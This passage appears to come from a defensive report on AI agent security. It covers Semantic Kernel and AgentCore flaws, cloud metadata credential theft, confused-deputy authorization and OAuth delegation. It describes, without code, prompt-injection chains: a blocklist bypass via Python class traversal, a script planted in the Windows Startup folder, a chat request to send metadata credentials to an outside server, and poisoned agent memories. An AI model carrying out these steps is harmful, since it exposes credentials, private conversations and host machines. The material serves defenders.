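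AWS advised customers to upgrade. For those who could not, it recommended in its June bulletin a fixed list of approved package names in the application's code. In the July bulletin, it told them not to pass "untrusted or model-generated input" to the function at all, or to validate names against the strict rules of PyPI, the public library of Python packages. These workarounds are worth keeping after the upgrade, because the new version makes the shell treat a package name as a name but does not ensure that the package is safe. Pip can run a package's own setup code during installation, so an attacker who can choose the name could upload a malicious package to PyPI and have the agent install it, even with no flaw in the SDK.

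BeyondTrust also advised customers to attach no execution role when the code does not need AWS access, to keep the role's permissions narrow when it does, and to monitor what Code Interpreter runs.

The same team had earlier found a similar weakness in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, where lax input validation put users' GitHub access tokens at risk. OpenAI has fixed it, according to MEA Tech Watch's *AI Coding Agent Flaw Exposed*.

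### Two flaws in Semantic Kernel

In May 2026, Microsoft published details of two flaws in Semantic Kernel that let an attacker use prompt injection to run code on the computer hosting the agent. Microsoft had already fixed both.

The first was in a search tool. Microsoft's researchers built a demonstration agent that finds hotels. When a user asked for hotels in Paris, the model called the search function with `Paris` as the city. The framework inserted that word into a line of Python, `lambda x: x.city == 'Paris'`, and ran the line with `eval()`, which executes text as code. An attacker could use a quotation mark in the city name to end the value early and then add their own Python, as with the false order number in SQL.

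The framework's developers had foreseen this and added three protections, but the researchers got past all of them. The code accepted only a lambda expression (a small unnamed function), rejected a list of dangerous names such as `eval`, `exec` and `open`, and ran the expression without Python's built-in functions.

- They placed their code inside a valid lambda expression, which satisfied the first check.
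- They used names that the blocklist lacked, including `load_module` and `system`.
- They needed no built-in functions because they started from a basic Python value and followed the links between Python's classes until they reached one that can import modules.

A single prompt then opened the calculator on the machine running the agent. This test shows that a model can be made to pass a long and very odd-looking city name to the tool unchanged, which a test that passes a crafted value straight to a function would not show.

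The flaw affects the Python version of Semantic Kernel before 1.39.4, and only agents whose search tool uses the in-memory data store with its default filter. The attacker must also be able to get text into the agent's input. Microsoft's fix mostly replaces the list of forbidden names with lists of permitted ones. The filter may now contain comparisons, simple logic, arithmetic and fixed values, and it can call only approved functions. This is much stronger, but it is more complex than necessary for checking whether two city names match, since ordinary code can compare the strings directly without running either as code.

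The second flaw was an unchecked file path in a Semantic Kernel plugin that runs Python in a cloud sandbox. The plugin has helper functions that move files between the sandbox and the computer running the agent. In the .NET version, a developer had accidentally marked the download helper, `DownloadFileAsync`, as a tool. The model could therefore call it and choose where on the computer to save the file, and no code checked the location.

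An attacker could combine this with a tool that the model was supposed to have. One injected instruction made the agent write a malicious script inside the sandbox, where it could not harm the host computer. Another made the agent download the script into the Windows Startup folder, so Windows would run it the next time the user signed in. Each call was a normal use of a working tool, and the download path was an ordinary one to a real folder.

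The upload helper accepted any local path in both the Python and .NET versions, so an injection could make the agent copy private keys from the computer into the sandbox.

Microsoft removed the label from the download helper in version 1.71.0 of the .NET SDK, so the model can no longer call the function. It also added a check for developers who still call the function from their own code. The check converts the path to its full form, then compares it with a list of permitted folders. The conversion has to come first because a path such as `downloads/../startup` begins with a permitted folder but leads to a different one. Microsoft describes the similar protections for uploads as opt-in, so developers have to turn them on themselves.

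Microsoft attributes both flaws to the agent's architecture and tool design, since the model turned a request into a structured call, as it was built to do. That is a fair account of the model's role, but the misplaced label was also a coding mistake, and deleting it was enough to break the attack.

### A package name and four layers of validation

Developers can validate an argument at four layers: its type, its form, how the tool passes it to the next program, and whether it fits the task. Suppose a user asks an agent to chart last month's sales from a spreadsheet, and the agent needs the data-analysis package `pandas`. The table shows how each layer, working alone, would handle six values that the model might pass to an installation tool.

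| Value | Type and schema | Strict name pattern | Safe interface | Fit with the task |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A number in place of text | Rejects | Rejects | May cause an error | Rejects |
| `pandas`, a line break and a command | Accepts | Rejects | Makes the command harmless | Rejects |
| `pandas[...]` with a shell command in the brackets | Accepts | Rejects | Makes the command harmless | Rejects |
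| The option `--index-url` with an attacker's address | Accepts | Rejects | Accepts | Rejects |
| A misspelling of `pandas` that an attacker has registered | Accepts | Accepts | Accepts | Rejects |
| `pandas`, if an attacker has tampered with the latest release | Accepts | Accepts | Accepts | Accepts |

The tool's schema might require a list of strings, each no longer than a hundred characters. This catches malformed calls, and many model providers can force a model's output to follow a schema. But a package name followed by a command still passes if it is short enough. JSON also has a standard way to write a line break inside a string, so parsing preserves a malicious name that contains one.

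A schema describes the form of a value, but the harm depends on who chose the value and what the next program does with it. The path to the Startup folder is a valid string, and 4418 is a valid order number even if the order belongs to another customer. A developer can tighten a schema by listing every permitted value, which works well for fields like shipping method. Doing the same for package names means building an allowlist.

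An allowlist can restrict the format of package names or permit only specific packages. A PyPI name must begin and end with a letter or digit and may contain only letters, digits, periods, hyphens and underscores. A pattern that enforces this rule on the whole string rejects the line break and the pip option. Extras in brackets need a separate rule, and AWS suggests allowing only comma-separated identifiers. The developer should also convert names to a standard form before comparing them with a list, since PyPI treats `Scikit_Learn` and `scikit-learn` as the same package.

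Checks on the form of an argument often fail because the checker and the interpreter parse the same text differently. The security company Adversa AI found that attackers could get past the command filters of 10 out of 11 popular open-source agents because the shell rewrites a command after the filter has approved it (SC Media, *Shell injection flaw found in 10 of 11 open-source AI agents*, 2026). Even a perfect pattern check accepts any well-formed package name, including a misspelt one. A fixed list of approved packages would block the misspelt name. Such a list suits an agent that produces sales reports, but a general coding agent will keep needing packages that aren't on it.

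With a safe interface, developers don't have to guess how a shell will read the package name. The tool starts pip directly and passes `install` and `pandas` as separate arguments, so no shell is involved and a line break has no special meaning. Parameterised queries do the same for databases. AWS's final fix is weaker because the SDK still builds a shell command as text and relies on quotation marks to keep each name a single argument. Quoting works if developers apply it everywhere, but BentoML's developers did not.

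Even without a shell, however, pip treats `--index-url` as an option, so a safe interface does not replace the name pattern. Pip also cannot distinguish a useful package from a malicious one.

The check against the task determines whether the job needs the package. Code can determine this only if someone has already listed what the job needs. For sales charts, the developer can prepare a short list. A coding agent could install only the packages in a project file that a person has reviewed. The list should exist before the agent reads any untrusted text, because otherwise a sentence in the spreadsheet could cause the model to add a package to it. For the support agent, the equivalent check compares the customer on the order with the customer on the ticket, which would protect order 4418. A policy gate, ordinary code that every tool call must pass, can apply rules like these to all of an agent's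 tools.

None of the four layers helps if the intended package is itself malicious. Markovic (2026) reported in *Credential stealer slipped into Microsoft's official Python agent framework* that attackers added a credential stealer to two of Microsoft's official releases on PyPI in November 2026. The stealer searched for secrets from Azure, GitHub Actions and automated build systems. A developer's agent would have had good reason to install the package, and its name was correct. Developers can reduce this risk by specifying the exact version and its hash, so that pip rejects a release that nobody has reviewed. If a malicious release is still installed, the damage depends on which credentials are available in the sandbox.

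## Service accounts that reach further than the agent's task

An attacker who can run a command in an agent's sandbox, or just make the agent open a web address, can often obtain the credentials of the agent's service account. The account's permissions then determine which resources the attacker can use. In 2025 and 2026, security researchers found that Amazon and Google both gave agents default accounts that could read far more than the agents needed.

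### Credentials from the metadata service

A program on a cloud server, such as an AI agent, needs credentials to open a database or a file store. Cloud providers offer a metadata service that supplies them, so developers don't have to write a password into the code. Anyone who copied that code could use the password until somebody changed it. On AWS, the metadata service is at 169.254.169.254, an address that only works from inside the same virtual machine.

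1. An administrator or a setup tool creates a role (AWS's form of service account) and assigns it to the agent. The role lists the actions it permits and the resources they apply to.
2. The agent's code sends a web request to the metadata address.
3. The metadata service returns temporary credentials: an access key ID, a secret access key and a session token.
4. The agent signs its requests to AWS with these values. For each request, AWS looks up the role's permissions and allows or refuses the action.

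The metadata service does not check which program sent the request in step 2, or why. AWS's documentation warns that any code or actor inside the virtual machine can retrieve the role's credentials, according to *AWS Bedrock AgentCore Flaw Allowed Attackers to Hijack AI Agents* (Eswar, 2026).

Suppose the online shop gives its support agent a tool that opens couriers' tracking pages. A customer claims that the tracking page for a late parcel is at the metadata address and asks the agent to copy out its contents. The tool runs inside the virtual machine, so the request succeeds and the agent's reply contains the shop's credentials. This is called server-side request forgery, an attack in which the attacker chooses an address and a machine with more access than the attacker has makes the request.

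The attacker can now use the credentials on another computer and send requests straight to AWS, without going through the agent. It no longer matters whether the model would refuse to look up payroll data or whether the agent has a tool for it. Only the permission check in step 4 still applies, so the attacker can read the payroll files if the role can.

A well-trained model may refuse to open the metadata address, which makes the theft less likely, but the model has no effect on what the stolen credentials can do.

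### Agent God Mode and AgentCorruption

The starter toolkit for Amazon Bedrock AgentCore, AWS's agent platform, sets up a new agent with a single command. It creates a runtime, a memory store, a repository for the agent's container image (a packaged copy of its code and files) and an execution role. On 17 November 2025, Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, reported to AWS that these roles also gave access to other agents' resources, a problem it named Agent God Mode.

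The cause was a wildcard in the toolkit's AWS role. AWS permissions identify a resource by its path, and an asterisk in the path matches any name. An agent needs to read its own memory, but the role let it read `memory/*`, which covers every agent's memory in the account. Unit 42 found similar wildcards for four kinds of resource.

| Resource | What the role allowed | What an attacker gains |
|---|---|---|
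| Memories | Reading and changing any agent's memory | Other users' conversations, and a way to plant false memories |
| Container images | Downloading any image in the account | Source code and internal files, including those of programs unrelated to agents |
| Code interpreters | Running code in any interpreter | The permissions of that interpreter's own role |
| Runtimes | Starting any other agent | The help of an agent with more privileges |

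To open another agent's memory, an attacker also needed its identifier, which ended in a random string. The string gave little protection, because Unit 42 was able to use the compromised agent's role to download the target's container image, which contained the identifier in a text file. An attacker with the identifier could then read or alter the target's conversation history.

The access described in the last two rows of the table makes it hard to see what an agent can reach. A code interpreter runs under its own role, separate from the calling agent's role. If the finance team's interpreter can read the company's accounts, a support agent that can run code in that interpreter can read them too, even though its own role does not grant that access. An administrator therefore has to trace which agents and interpreters a role can call, and what each of those can do in turn.

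AWS sent Unit 42 its clarifications on 28 January 2026. Its security team said that the automatic roles had a "flat permission structure" and "should never be used in a production system". AWS also added a warning to its documentation that the roles were meant for development and testing.

By then AWS had two more reports. Zenity, the agent security company, had written on 25 December 2025 about access to the metadata service, and on 12 January 2026 about the breadth of the default role. On 8 October 2026, it published the complete attack under the name AgentCorruption. Cornelißen and Eswar describe how it worked:

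1. The researchers built a simple agent with a ready-made tool for web requests. In the chat, they asked it to fetch the metadata and send the result to their server, and the agent did so. A tool for running shell commands worked just as well.
2. They loaded the stolen credentials on their own machine and checked with AWS which role they now held.
3. They listed the platform's log groups, whose names revealed the identifiers of every agent and memory in the region.
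4. They downloaded other agents' container images, called internal agents that were never meant to be public, read private conversations and retrieved the keys to connected services.
5. They wrote entries into other agents' long-term memory that told those agents to open an attacker's web address before each reply and follow the instructions there.

MemGhost, the email attack on agents' memories, needed a specially trained model to write a message that an agent would save. In AgentCorruption, the stolen role let the researchers write to the memory directly. The entries they planted remain after the stolen credentials stop working.

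The permissions over memories, images and runtimes match those Unit 42 reported in November. Zenity's main addition was the first step of the attack, obtaining the credentials with one chat message. It also found that the role could read stored secrets and that the log names revealed the identifiers, so an attacker didn't have to search container images for them. The attack covered all the AgentCore agents in one AWS account and geographical region.

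In Google's Dialogflow CX, a developer could affect other agents because they all ran code in one shared environment. Each AgentCore agent had its own virtual machine, but the role let it reach the others through AWS's normal interfaces without breaking out of that machine. Zenity blamed the platform rather than the tool for the first step, since any tool that can send web traffic can reach the metadata service.

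AWS made that step harder on 14 February 2026, when AgentCore began starting all new agents with only the second version of the metadata service, IMDSv2. The older version answered the same simple kind of request a browser uses to open a page. With IMDSv2, a program must first send a PUT request to get a token, then include that token when it asks for the credentials. A tool that only opens pages cannot do this, but a shell can, and so can a web tool that lets the model choose the request type and headers.

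AWS took longer to restrict the role's permissions. On 25 February, it told Zenity that it was working on the underlying cause, and on 12 April it closed the report about metadata access as "informative". Zenity checked the role on 22 June, more than five months after reporting its permissions, and found them unchanged. When Zenity checked again on 29 September, the role could no longer call other agents, read their private conversations or retrieve secrets from AWS Secrets Manager, and AWS had narrowed other permissions. Zenity does not know the exact date of the change.

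AWS disputes that there was a vulnerability. Cornelißen quotes a spokesperson saying that the research showed "expected and documented behavior". Eswar reports that this response referred to the metadata access, and that AWS says access to another account requires explicit authorisation. Zenity called its findings "a Chain of AWS AgentCore Flaws" in the headline of its press release.

AWS has a reasonable case on metadata access, because programs have to get credentials from somewhere and AWS's ordinary rented servers use the same method. Its case on the default role is much weaker, because AWS had already told Unit 42 that nobody should use such a role in production, and it later removed the permissions that Zenity had complained about. Behavior can also be "expected and documented" and still reflect an architectural flaw. The metadata service and the permission check both worked as AWS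 had specified, and together they let one chatbot read every other agent's conversations.

Zenity sells a security product for AgentCore, so it has a commercial reason to prefer the stronger wording. Its demonstration also started from an agent that the researchers had built. The demonstration shows how far an attacker could get once an agent complied, but not how often a company's deployed chatbot would comply. In an Italian article on AgentCorruption, Dario Fadda (2026) reported no known attacks outside the research.

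Customers who deployed agents before the change should check their roles, because a new default does not necessarily change existing ones. Mitigant's *AgentCore or AgentSore* reproduces the problem in one account with a victim agent and a malicious agent that holds the toolkit's wildcard role. It says users are now advised to switch from the starter toolkit to AWS's newer AgentCore command-line tool.

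### Google's default service agent

Unit 42's *Double Agents* describes a similar default in Vertex AI, Google Cloud's platform for building and running agents. The researchers deployed an agent that was malicious from the start. Whenever anyone called it, one of its tools queried Google's metadata service and returned the credentials it received. This resembles a company installing a stranger's ready-made agent more than it resembles prompt injection, but an attacker who obtained the same credentials through a legitimate agent could have used them the same way.

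The credentials belonged to a service agent, a service account that Google creates and manages for the customer. By default, it could list and read every storage bucket in the customer's Google Cloud project. Buckets hold files of any kind, from product photos to database backups. If the shop ran its support agent in such a project, someone who stole the agent's credentials could read the backups even though nobody had connected them to the agent. Unit 42 headed this part of its study "From Agent to Storage Admin", which slightly overstates the result, because the access it describes was read-only.

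The same credentials also gave access to some of Google's own resources. The researchers downloaded private container images that form the core of the service behind Vertex AI's agents. An ordinary customer account could not open these images. The researchers also learned the names of other restricted images and could read deployment files in the separate project that Google maintains for each deployed agent.

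The stolen credentials could not, however, open a restricted Google bucket named in one deployment file. Google confirmed that the service agent could not alter Google's production images, so an attacker could not have planted code in other customers' agents this way. One of the deployment files used pickle, a Python format that can run code when loaded, but Unit 42 did not test whether an attacker could exploit it.

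Another limit protected the customer's email and documents. Reading someone's email requires a matching permission for the account as well as the right OAuth scope, and Google did not grant that permission by default. Scopes list the services a token may be used with. The agent's default scopes included Gmail, Google Calendar and Google Drive, and customers could not edit them.

Unit 42 calls this an effective boundary but still considers the scopes a structural weakness. That seems fair, because the token would not provide a second barrier if an administrator later gave the agent access to one shared folder and made a mistake in the permissions. The scopes are still a smaller problem than the access to the buckets, which required no such mistake.

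Google responded by documenting more clearly which accounts and resources Vertex AI uses. It also changed the deployment process, so the researchers' original code may no longer work. Its main advice to customers was to use Bring Your Own Service Account, an option in which the customer creates a dedicated account for the agent and grants it only the permissions the agent needs. This is good advice, but it doesn't help customers who don't know about the default account.

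### How much a shared role adds to the risk

A calculation shows the effect of a role that covers many agents. Suppose a company has 20 agents, one of which handles the payroll, and each has a 2% chance of being taken over in a given year, independently of the others.

If each agent's role covers only its own data, a takeover exposes the payroll data only when the attacker takes over the payroll agent. The probability is 2%. If all the agents share a wildcard role, any of the 20 will do. The probability that none of them falls is 0.98 multiplied by itself 20 times, or about 0.67, so the payroll data is exposed with probability

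1 − 0.98^20 ≈ 0.33

or about 33%. The table adds a middle case in which the company divides its agents into four groups of five, each with its own role.

| Arrangement | Yearly chance that a given agent's data is exposed | Average number of agents exposed per year |
|---|---|---|
| A separate role for each agent | 2% | 0.4 |
| Four roles, each shared by five agents | 9.6% | 1.9 |
| One wildcard role for all 20 | 33% | 6.6 |

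The first takeover exposes everything under the wildcard role but only one agent's data under separate roles. Separate roles don't make a takeover less likely, since the chance that an attacker takes over at least one agent during the year is 33% in every row.

Better resistance to prompt injection still leaves a large risk if the role stays broad. Suppose a new model halves the chance of a takeover to 1% per agent. With the wildcard role, the payroll data still has an 18% chance of being exposed, nine times the chance with separate roles and the old model. The chance of a takeover would have to fall to about 0.1% per agent before the wildcard role was as safe as separate roles are with the old model.

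Real agents also differ in how exposed they are. Suppose the company's public chatbot has a 20% chance of being taken over and the 19 internal agents have 0.5% each. The risk to the payroll data is then 0.5% with separate roles and 27% with the wildcard role. About two thirds of the increase comes from the chatbot, which has nothing to do with payroll. In AgentCorruption, a conversation with a public agent led to internal ones in the same way.

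Assuming independence may overstate the benefit of separate roles. A company's agents often use the same model and tools, so a prompt that works on one may work on the others. If an attacker can take over either all 20 agents or none, the payroll data has the same 2% risk under both arrangements. Most companies are probably between this extreme and full independence, because an internal agent that reads no outside text is harder to reach even if it uses the same model as the public chatbot.

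### Narrowing the role and protecting its credentials

Giving each agent its own role is the obvious remedy, but it is not enough by itself. AWS's toolkit could create an execution role for each agent it set up, and an attacker could still move between agents because each role contained wildcards. The permissions also have to name their resources. For the support agent's memory, the difference looks like this, with an invented identifier in the second line:

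`memory/*`

`memory/support-agent-7Kq2`

The support agent's role would also list only its own container image and the one secret it needs, perhaps the key to the email service. It would not allow the agent to start other agents. If the shop later wants the support agent to call the refund agent, the administrator can add permission for that one agent, and anyone reviewing the role will see the connection.

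Limiting a role to named resources is much easier than working out which order the agent needs to open for a particular ticket, because the developers already know which memory store belongs to the agent. With such a role, the agent can still read every customer's orders, because it needs the order table for its work, but the attacker can't get into the rest of the company's systems.

Separate cloud accounts provide a stronger boundary. Neither AgentCorruption nor Agent God Mode crossed from one AWS account to another, which AWS says requires explicit authorisation. A company could therefore put its public chatbot in one account and its payroll agent in another. A wildcard left in the chatbot's role would then expose fewer resources. However, the company would have more accounts to manage and would need to set up explicit links between agents that work together.

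Short-lived credentials help less. AgentCore's credentials expire within hours, but an attacker with a prepared script can download a container image or a conversation history in minutes. The attacker can also request new credentials from the metadata service as long as the agent keeps following the attacker's instructions. Short lifetimes help most when someone later finds credentials in a log file or an old backup. Administrators can also restrict a role to the company's own network, which makes stolen credentials harder to use elsewhere.

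Developers can also block the metadata address. If the web tool does the blocking, it has to check the destination address after looking up the domain name and again after every redirect. Otherwise an attacker can register a harmless-looking domain that leads to the metadata service. A check in the web tool also doesn't stop a shell tool on the same machine from reaching the metadata service, so a firewall rule that covers every tool is more reliable.

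But the agent's own code may need the metadata service to get its credentials. One solution is to run the tools in a separate sandbox that has no role and keep the credentials outside it, in the orchestration layer, which makes the few AWS requests the agent needs. This would also have reduced the damage from the AgentCore SDK flaws, which, as Mascellino reported, exposed credentials available inside the sandbox.

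Blocking the address prevents credential theft, but an attacker can still misuse the agent through its normal tools. If the order tool can read the whole table, a prompt injection can make it do so. A narrow role limits both kinds of attack, so it is the better choice if a company has time for only one change.

### Why broad defaults persist

A broad role lets a new agent work at the first attempt. With a narrow one, the developer may get an "access denied" message and have to find out which of dozens of permissions is missing. A starter toolkit is meant to spare people this work, and Unit 42 says AWS's default configuration favoured easy deployment over strict least privilege. Wildcards also make the toolkit easier to build. A memory has no full identifier until the platform creates it, so a tool that names the identifier in its permissions has to create the resources first and write the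 permissions afterwards.

The broad role then tends to stay in place. Fadda compares AgentCore's default to the "provisional" roles that companies create to get a service running and never restrict. As Saltzer and Schroeder warned, normal use does not reveal excess access. Narrowing the role also risks an outage and brings no visible benefit.

Documentation does not correct this very well. The people who rely most on an automatic setup often know the least about cloud permissions, and they are unlikely to look for a warning about a role they did not create. Mitigant points out that organisations that missed AWS's note at deployment are exposed in production. Relying on the note also means each customer has to fix a problem that AWS could fix for all of them.

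Some customers may have built agents that depend on the broad permissions, for instance to call one another, and a sudden restriction could break them. This might explain part of AWS's delay, although AWS has not said so. The risk gives cloud providers a reason to leave existing roles alone for a while, but it does not justify creating new ones with the same permissions. The restrictions Zenity found in September also suggest that most agents never needed the access.

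AWS has since previewed separate identities for individual agents at its re:Invent conference, according to KBY Technologies' *AWS IAM for Agents, Bedrock Gateway and Greenlight* (2026). These should make it easier to give each agent its own permissions and to see which agent made a request. How much they reduce an attacker's reach will depend largely on a new identity's default permissions.

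## Whose authority an agent acts with

If a customer asks a shop's support agent about someone else's order, the database returns the order because it checks only the agent's permissions. This is an example of the confused deputy problem, a nearly fifty-year-old flaw in which a program uses its own authority on behalf of someone who lacks it.

### Hardy's compiler

Norm Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) describes an incident from about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on its computers. Customers could run a compiler and name a file for its debugging output. The compiler also recorded statistics in a file called STAT, in the system folder SYSX, so the staff gave it permission to write to any file in that folder.

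The folder also held BILL, the company's billing records. A customer learned this name and gave it to the compiler as the file for debugging output. The customer had no right to change BILL, but the compiler did, so the operating system let it overwrite the records.

Hardy could not find a faulty line of code. The code that wrote the output was correct at first and became wrong only when the staff granted the compiler its licence. Making the compiler reject every file in SYSX would block anyone who had a legitimate reason to send output there, and rejecting only the name BILL would leave the folder's other sensitive files exposed. The problem was that the compiler had authority from two sources, its user and its licence, and no way to specify which one to use for a given file.

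Each part of the story has a counterpart in the shop.

| Tymshare | The shop |
|---|---|
| The compiler | The support agent |
| The customer who ran it | The customer who opened the ticket |
| The file name the customer supplied | The order number in the ticket |
| The licence to write in SYSX | The service account's permission to read the order table |
| BILL | Order 4418, which belongs to someone else |
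| The operating system | The database |

Agents make the problem harder in some ways. The compiler ran fixed code, so a programmer could in principle inspect every place where it wrote a file. As *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) points out, an agent's decisions depend on its prompt and can vary between runs. The harmful request may also be hidden in an email or document, and the authority may pass through several people, companies and agents before the final action.

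Tymshare first added a system call that let the compiler choose which authority to use. If it used the customer's authority, its request to open BILL would fail. But some programs soon needed more than two authorities, and Hardy came to prefer capabilities, which are unforgeable references that both identify a resource and grant permission to use it. The customer would give the compiler a capability for the output file instead of a name, and a customer with no right to BILL would not have a capability for it. In the shop, the ticket system could give the order tool a reference that opens only one customer's orders. The model could still call the tool with order number 4418, but the tool could not open that order.

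### The formal condition

Siu, He and colleagues (2026), in *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security*, define the confused deputy with a set of permissions R. Each entry in R is a pair, such as an agent and a database it may use. When an agent's action accesses a target, the agent is a confused deputy if

(user, target) ∉ R and (agent, target) ∈ R

In words, the user who started the task lacks permission for the target, the agent has it, and the agent goes ahead.

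In their example, an employee asks the company's agent to show all employees' salaries. The employee is not allowed to open the human resources (HR) database, but the agent is, because it does administrative work there. If the agent runs the query, it meets the condition. The employee logged in properly, and no outsider planted any text.

*Proof-of-Continuity* (2026) adds the condition that the deputy must act because of the user's request. Without this condition, the agent would count as a confused deputy whenever it read the salaries for the monthly payroll while an ordinary employee happened to be logged in.

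The remedy is to require both permissions at once. The agent may open the salaries only if the user could open them too.

| Request for all salaries | User has permission | Agent has permission | Check the agent only | Check both |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Employee asks the HR agent | No | Yes | Allows | Refuses |
| HR director asks the HR agent | Yes | Yes | Allows | Allows |
| HR director asks the support agent | Yes | No | Refuses | Refuses |

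The user's identity has to come from the login session, not the model. If the tool call had a field for the user's name, an employee could try to persuade the model to enter the director's. Permissions also have to be finer than a single one for the whole database, so that an employee can see their own salary without seeing everyone else's.

Requiring both permissions would block some of the work an agent has to do. Hardy's compiler had to write to STAT, which customers were not supposed to touch, and the support agent may need to write to a log that customers cannot change. Developers therefore have to decide, for each operation, whether the agent is acting for the user or for the company.

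### What a list of tools leaves undecided

Common agent frameworks leave this decision to developers. In June 2026, *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) examined fixed versions of the public source code for LangChain and its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to the payment company Stripe. It looked for a default check that compares the values in each tool call with a policy and blocks the call if they do not match.

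All the frameworks let developers choose which tools an agent gets, but none had such a check. LangChain finds the tool by name, usually validates the form of the arguments, and runs it. A developer can add human approval, but the framework does not require it. LlamaIndex works much the same way. Stripe's toolkit has a list of permitted actions and relies on keys with limited permissions. Within those limits, it forwards whatever amount and customer the model supplies. Stripe's remote servers may run further checks, but the study did not cover them.

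Mellafe Zuvic then built a mock payment system with a tool for changing the account that receives a merchant's money. A fixed tool call simulated the output of a hijacked model and named an attacker's account. LangChain ran the call and changed the account, and a test with LlamaIndex showed the same gap. ScopeGate, Mellafe Zuvic's own policy gate, refused the same call because the attacker's account was not on a list of verified accounts.

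A merchant's agent may well need this tool, so removing it is not always an option. The tool list determines whether the agent can ever change a payout account, but not whether a particular account belongs to the merchant. In the shop, every customer's ticket goes to an agent with the same order tool, and having that tool does not determine whose orders the agent may open.

ScopeGate blocked all 48 hostile calls in a prepared set. It also blocked all 29 unauthorised calls from an attacking model that had 40 rounds and was told why each call was refused. It allowed all 10 legitimate calls. In another test, Latam-GPT, a Latin American model, attempted an unauthorised payout in all ten trials, and ScopeGate stopped every one. The same person wrote the gate and the tests, so a determined outsider might get past it. An earlier version let through a payment whose amount was NaN ("not a number"),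 a value that is never greater than any limit.

A companion benchmark measured how often models attempt unauthorised actions when injected text presents those actions as part of the user's task. The average rate was 60% for 12 cheaper models and 19% for 15 flagship models, although Gemini 3.1 Pro made no such attempts. The benchmark measured attempts in a sandbox, and newer models may do better.

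Dantuluri and Sundi (2026) reached a similar conclusion in *Delegation Without Trust*. They tested LangGraph, inspected the code of CrewAI and AutoGen, and found no built-in authorisation in any of the three frameworks. Both researchers work for VotalAI, which sells a product that fills this gap, but the frameworks do not claim to be authorisation systems.

A fixed list works for a merchant with one payout account. But the orders the support agent may open depend on who is asking, so the check also needs reliable information about the user.

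### Exchanging the user's token

A delegated credential carries this information. In OAuth, a widely used standard for giving programs limited access to someone's account, an authorisation server issues these credentials as tokens. *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, 2020) describes how a program can swap one token for another that suits the next service.

Suppose Ana manages a team at the shop and asks the HR agent for her team's average salary.

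1. Ana signs in, and the agent's orchestration layer receives a token that identifies her.
2. The orchestration layer sends this token to the authorisation server with a second token that identifies the agent. It asks for permission to read salaries in the HR database and nothing else.
3. The server validates both tokens. It can also check whether Ana's token lists this agent as one that may act for her. It then issues a narrower token that names them both.
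4. The orchestration layer sends the new token with its query. The HR database checks that the token is genuine, unexpired, meant for this database and valid for reading salaries. It then looks up Ana's own permissions and returns only her team's rows.
5. The token expires, perhaps after a minute. The agent needs a new one for any later query.

The contents of the new token could look like this:

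```
{
  "sub": "ana@shop.example",
  "act": { "sub": "hr-agent" },
  "aud": "https://hr.shop.example",
  "scope": "salary:read",
  "exp": 1796479260
}
```

The `sub` field identifies Ana, `act` identifies the agent acting for her, and `aud` identifies the service that should accept the token. The expiry time is in seconds since the start of 1970.

A program can also request a token that names only the user, which Jones and colleagues call impersonation. With such a token, the HR database could not distinguish the agent from Ana, so it could not enforce a rule that agents may never change salaries. Its log would also show the agent's queries as hers.

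The standard leaves much of the security to whoever sets up the system. Here, `salary:read` does not specify whose salaries, so the protection depends on the database looking up Ana's permissions in step 4. Cancelling Ana's original token does not automatically cancel the agent's token, which is a good reason to give the agent's token a short lifetime. OAuth also lacks a consistent way to represent agents and other delegated actors across its different kinds of token, according to *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* (McGuinness, 2026), a draft standard meant to supply one.

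### MCP's current rules

The July 2026 revision of the Model Context Protocol (MCP) bases its authorization rules on OAuth. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) requires a client to request each token for one named server, and the server to reject tokens issued for anyone else. A server that calls another service needs a separate token for it, because Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) forbids the server to pass on the client's token. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* explains that if servers forwarded tokens, the second service's logs could attribute a request to the wrong party, and an attacker who compromised one service could use its tokens at others.

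These rules prevent a token for one server from working at another, but they do not make a server check whether the user may see a particular order. Authorisation is also optional in MCP, and servers that a client runs as local programs normally take their credentials from the computer's environment. These could include a key that does not identify a user.

Another rule lets permissions build up. If a token does not cover an operation, the server can reply with the scopes the operation needs. The client should then request a new token with those scopes and all the scopes it requested before. This saves repeated approvals, but an agent that needed write access once will keep requesting it.

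Model Context Protocol's *Enterprise-Managed Authorization* describes an optional extension that companies can add so that employees do not have to approve each server themselves. The company's sign-in system checks its policy and issues a short-lived statement that a particular user may reach a particular server through a particular client. The client exchanges the statement for an access token. When an employee leaves, an administrator can revoke their access to every server from one place.

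MCP's documentation uses "confused deputy" mainly for an attack on the login process. Some MCP servers relay requests to an outside service under a single identity. After a user approves the relay once, the service may store a cookie and skip the consent screen next time. An attacker can register a new client with the relay and send the user a link. If the user opens it, the service finds the cookie and skips the consent screen, and the relay sends the login code to the attacker. To prevent this, the relay must get the user's consent for each client separately.

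### Agents with no user present

A nightly job that looks for late parcels has no signed-in user. One option is for it to keep acting for the person who set it up, using a refresh token to get new access tokens after the original expires. If that person moves to another department, the job should lose the access they lost, but this happens only if each service checks the person's current permissions.

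Alternatively, the agent can act on its own behalf, which MCP also allows. There are then no user permissions to combine with the agent's, so the agent's role is the only limit on what it can do and has to be as narrow as possible.

No employee is present when the support agent receives a ticket, but a customer may have signed in to open it. If so, the shop can issue a token for that customer, which would protect order 4418. If the ticket came from an unverified email address, the agent has no one's authority to act with and should not open any orders until the customer signs in.

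### Chains of agents

*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* traces how authority can grow as agents pass work to one another. A user asks one agent to summarise the invoices in an inbox, and one of the emails contains an instruction to make a payment. The agent passes the instruction to a finance agent, but not the restriction that the task was read-only. The finance agent calls a payment tool with a valid credential. The payment service correctly identifies the caller but cannot detect that the payment began with a stranger's email. *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) notes that developers generally do not train models to question the authority behind an instruction.

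One remedy is to ensure that authority can only shrink as agents delegate tasks. *DelegateGuard* (Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues, 2026) turns the user's authorisation into a capability that lists a purpose, the kinds of data involved, the permitted operations and destinations, and how many more times an agent may delegate. An agent can pass on part of its capability but cannot add to it.

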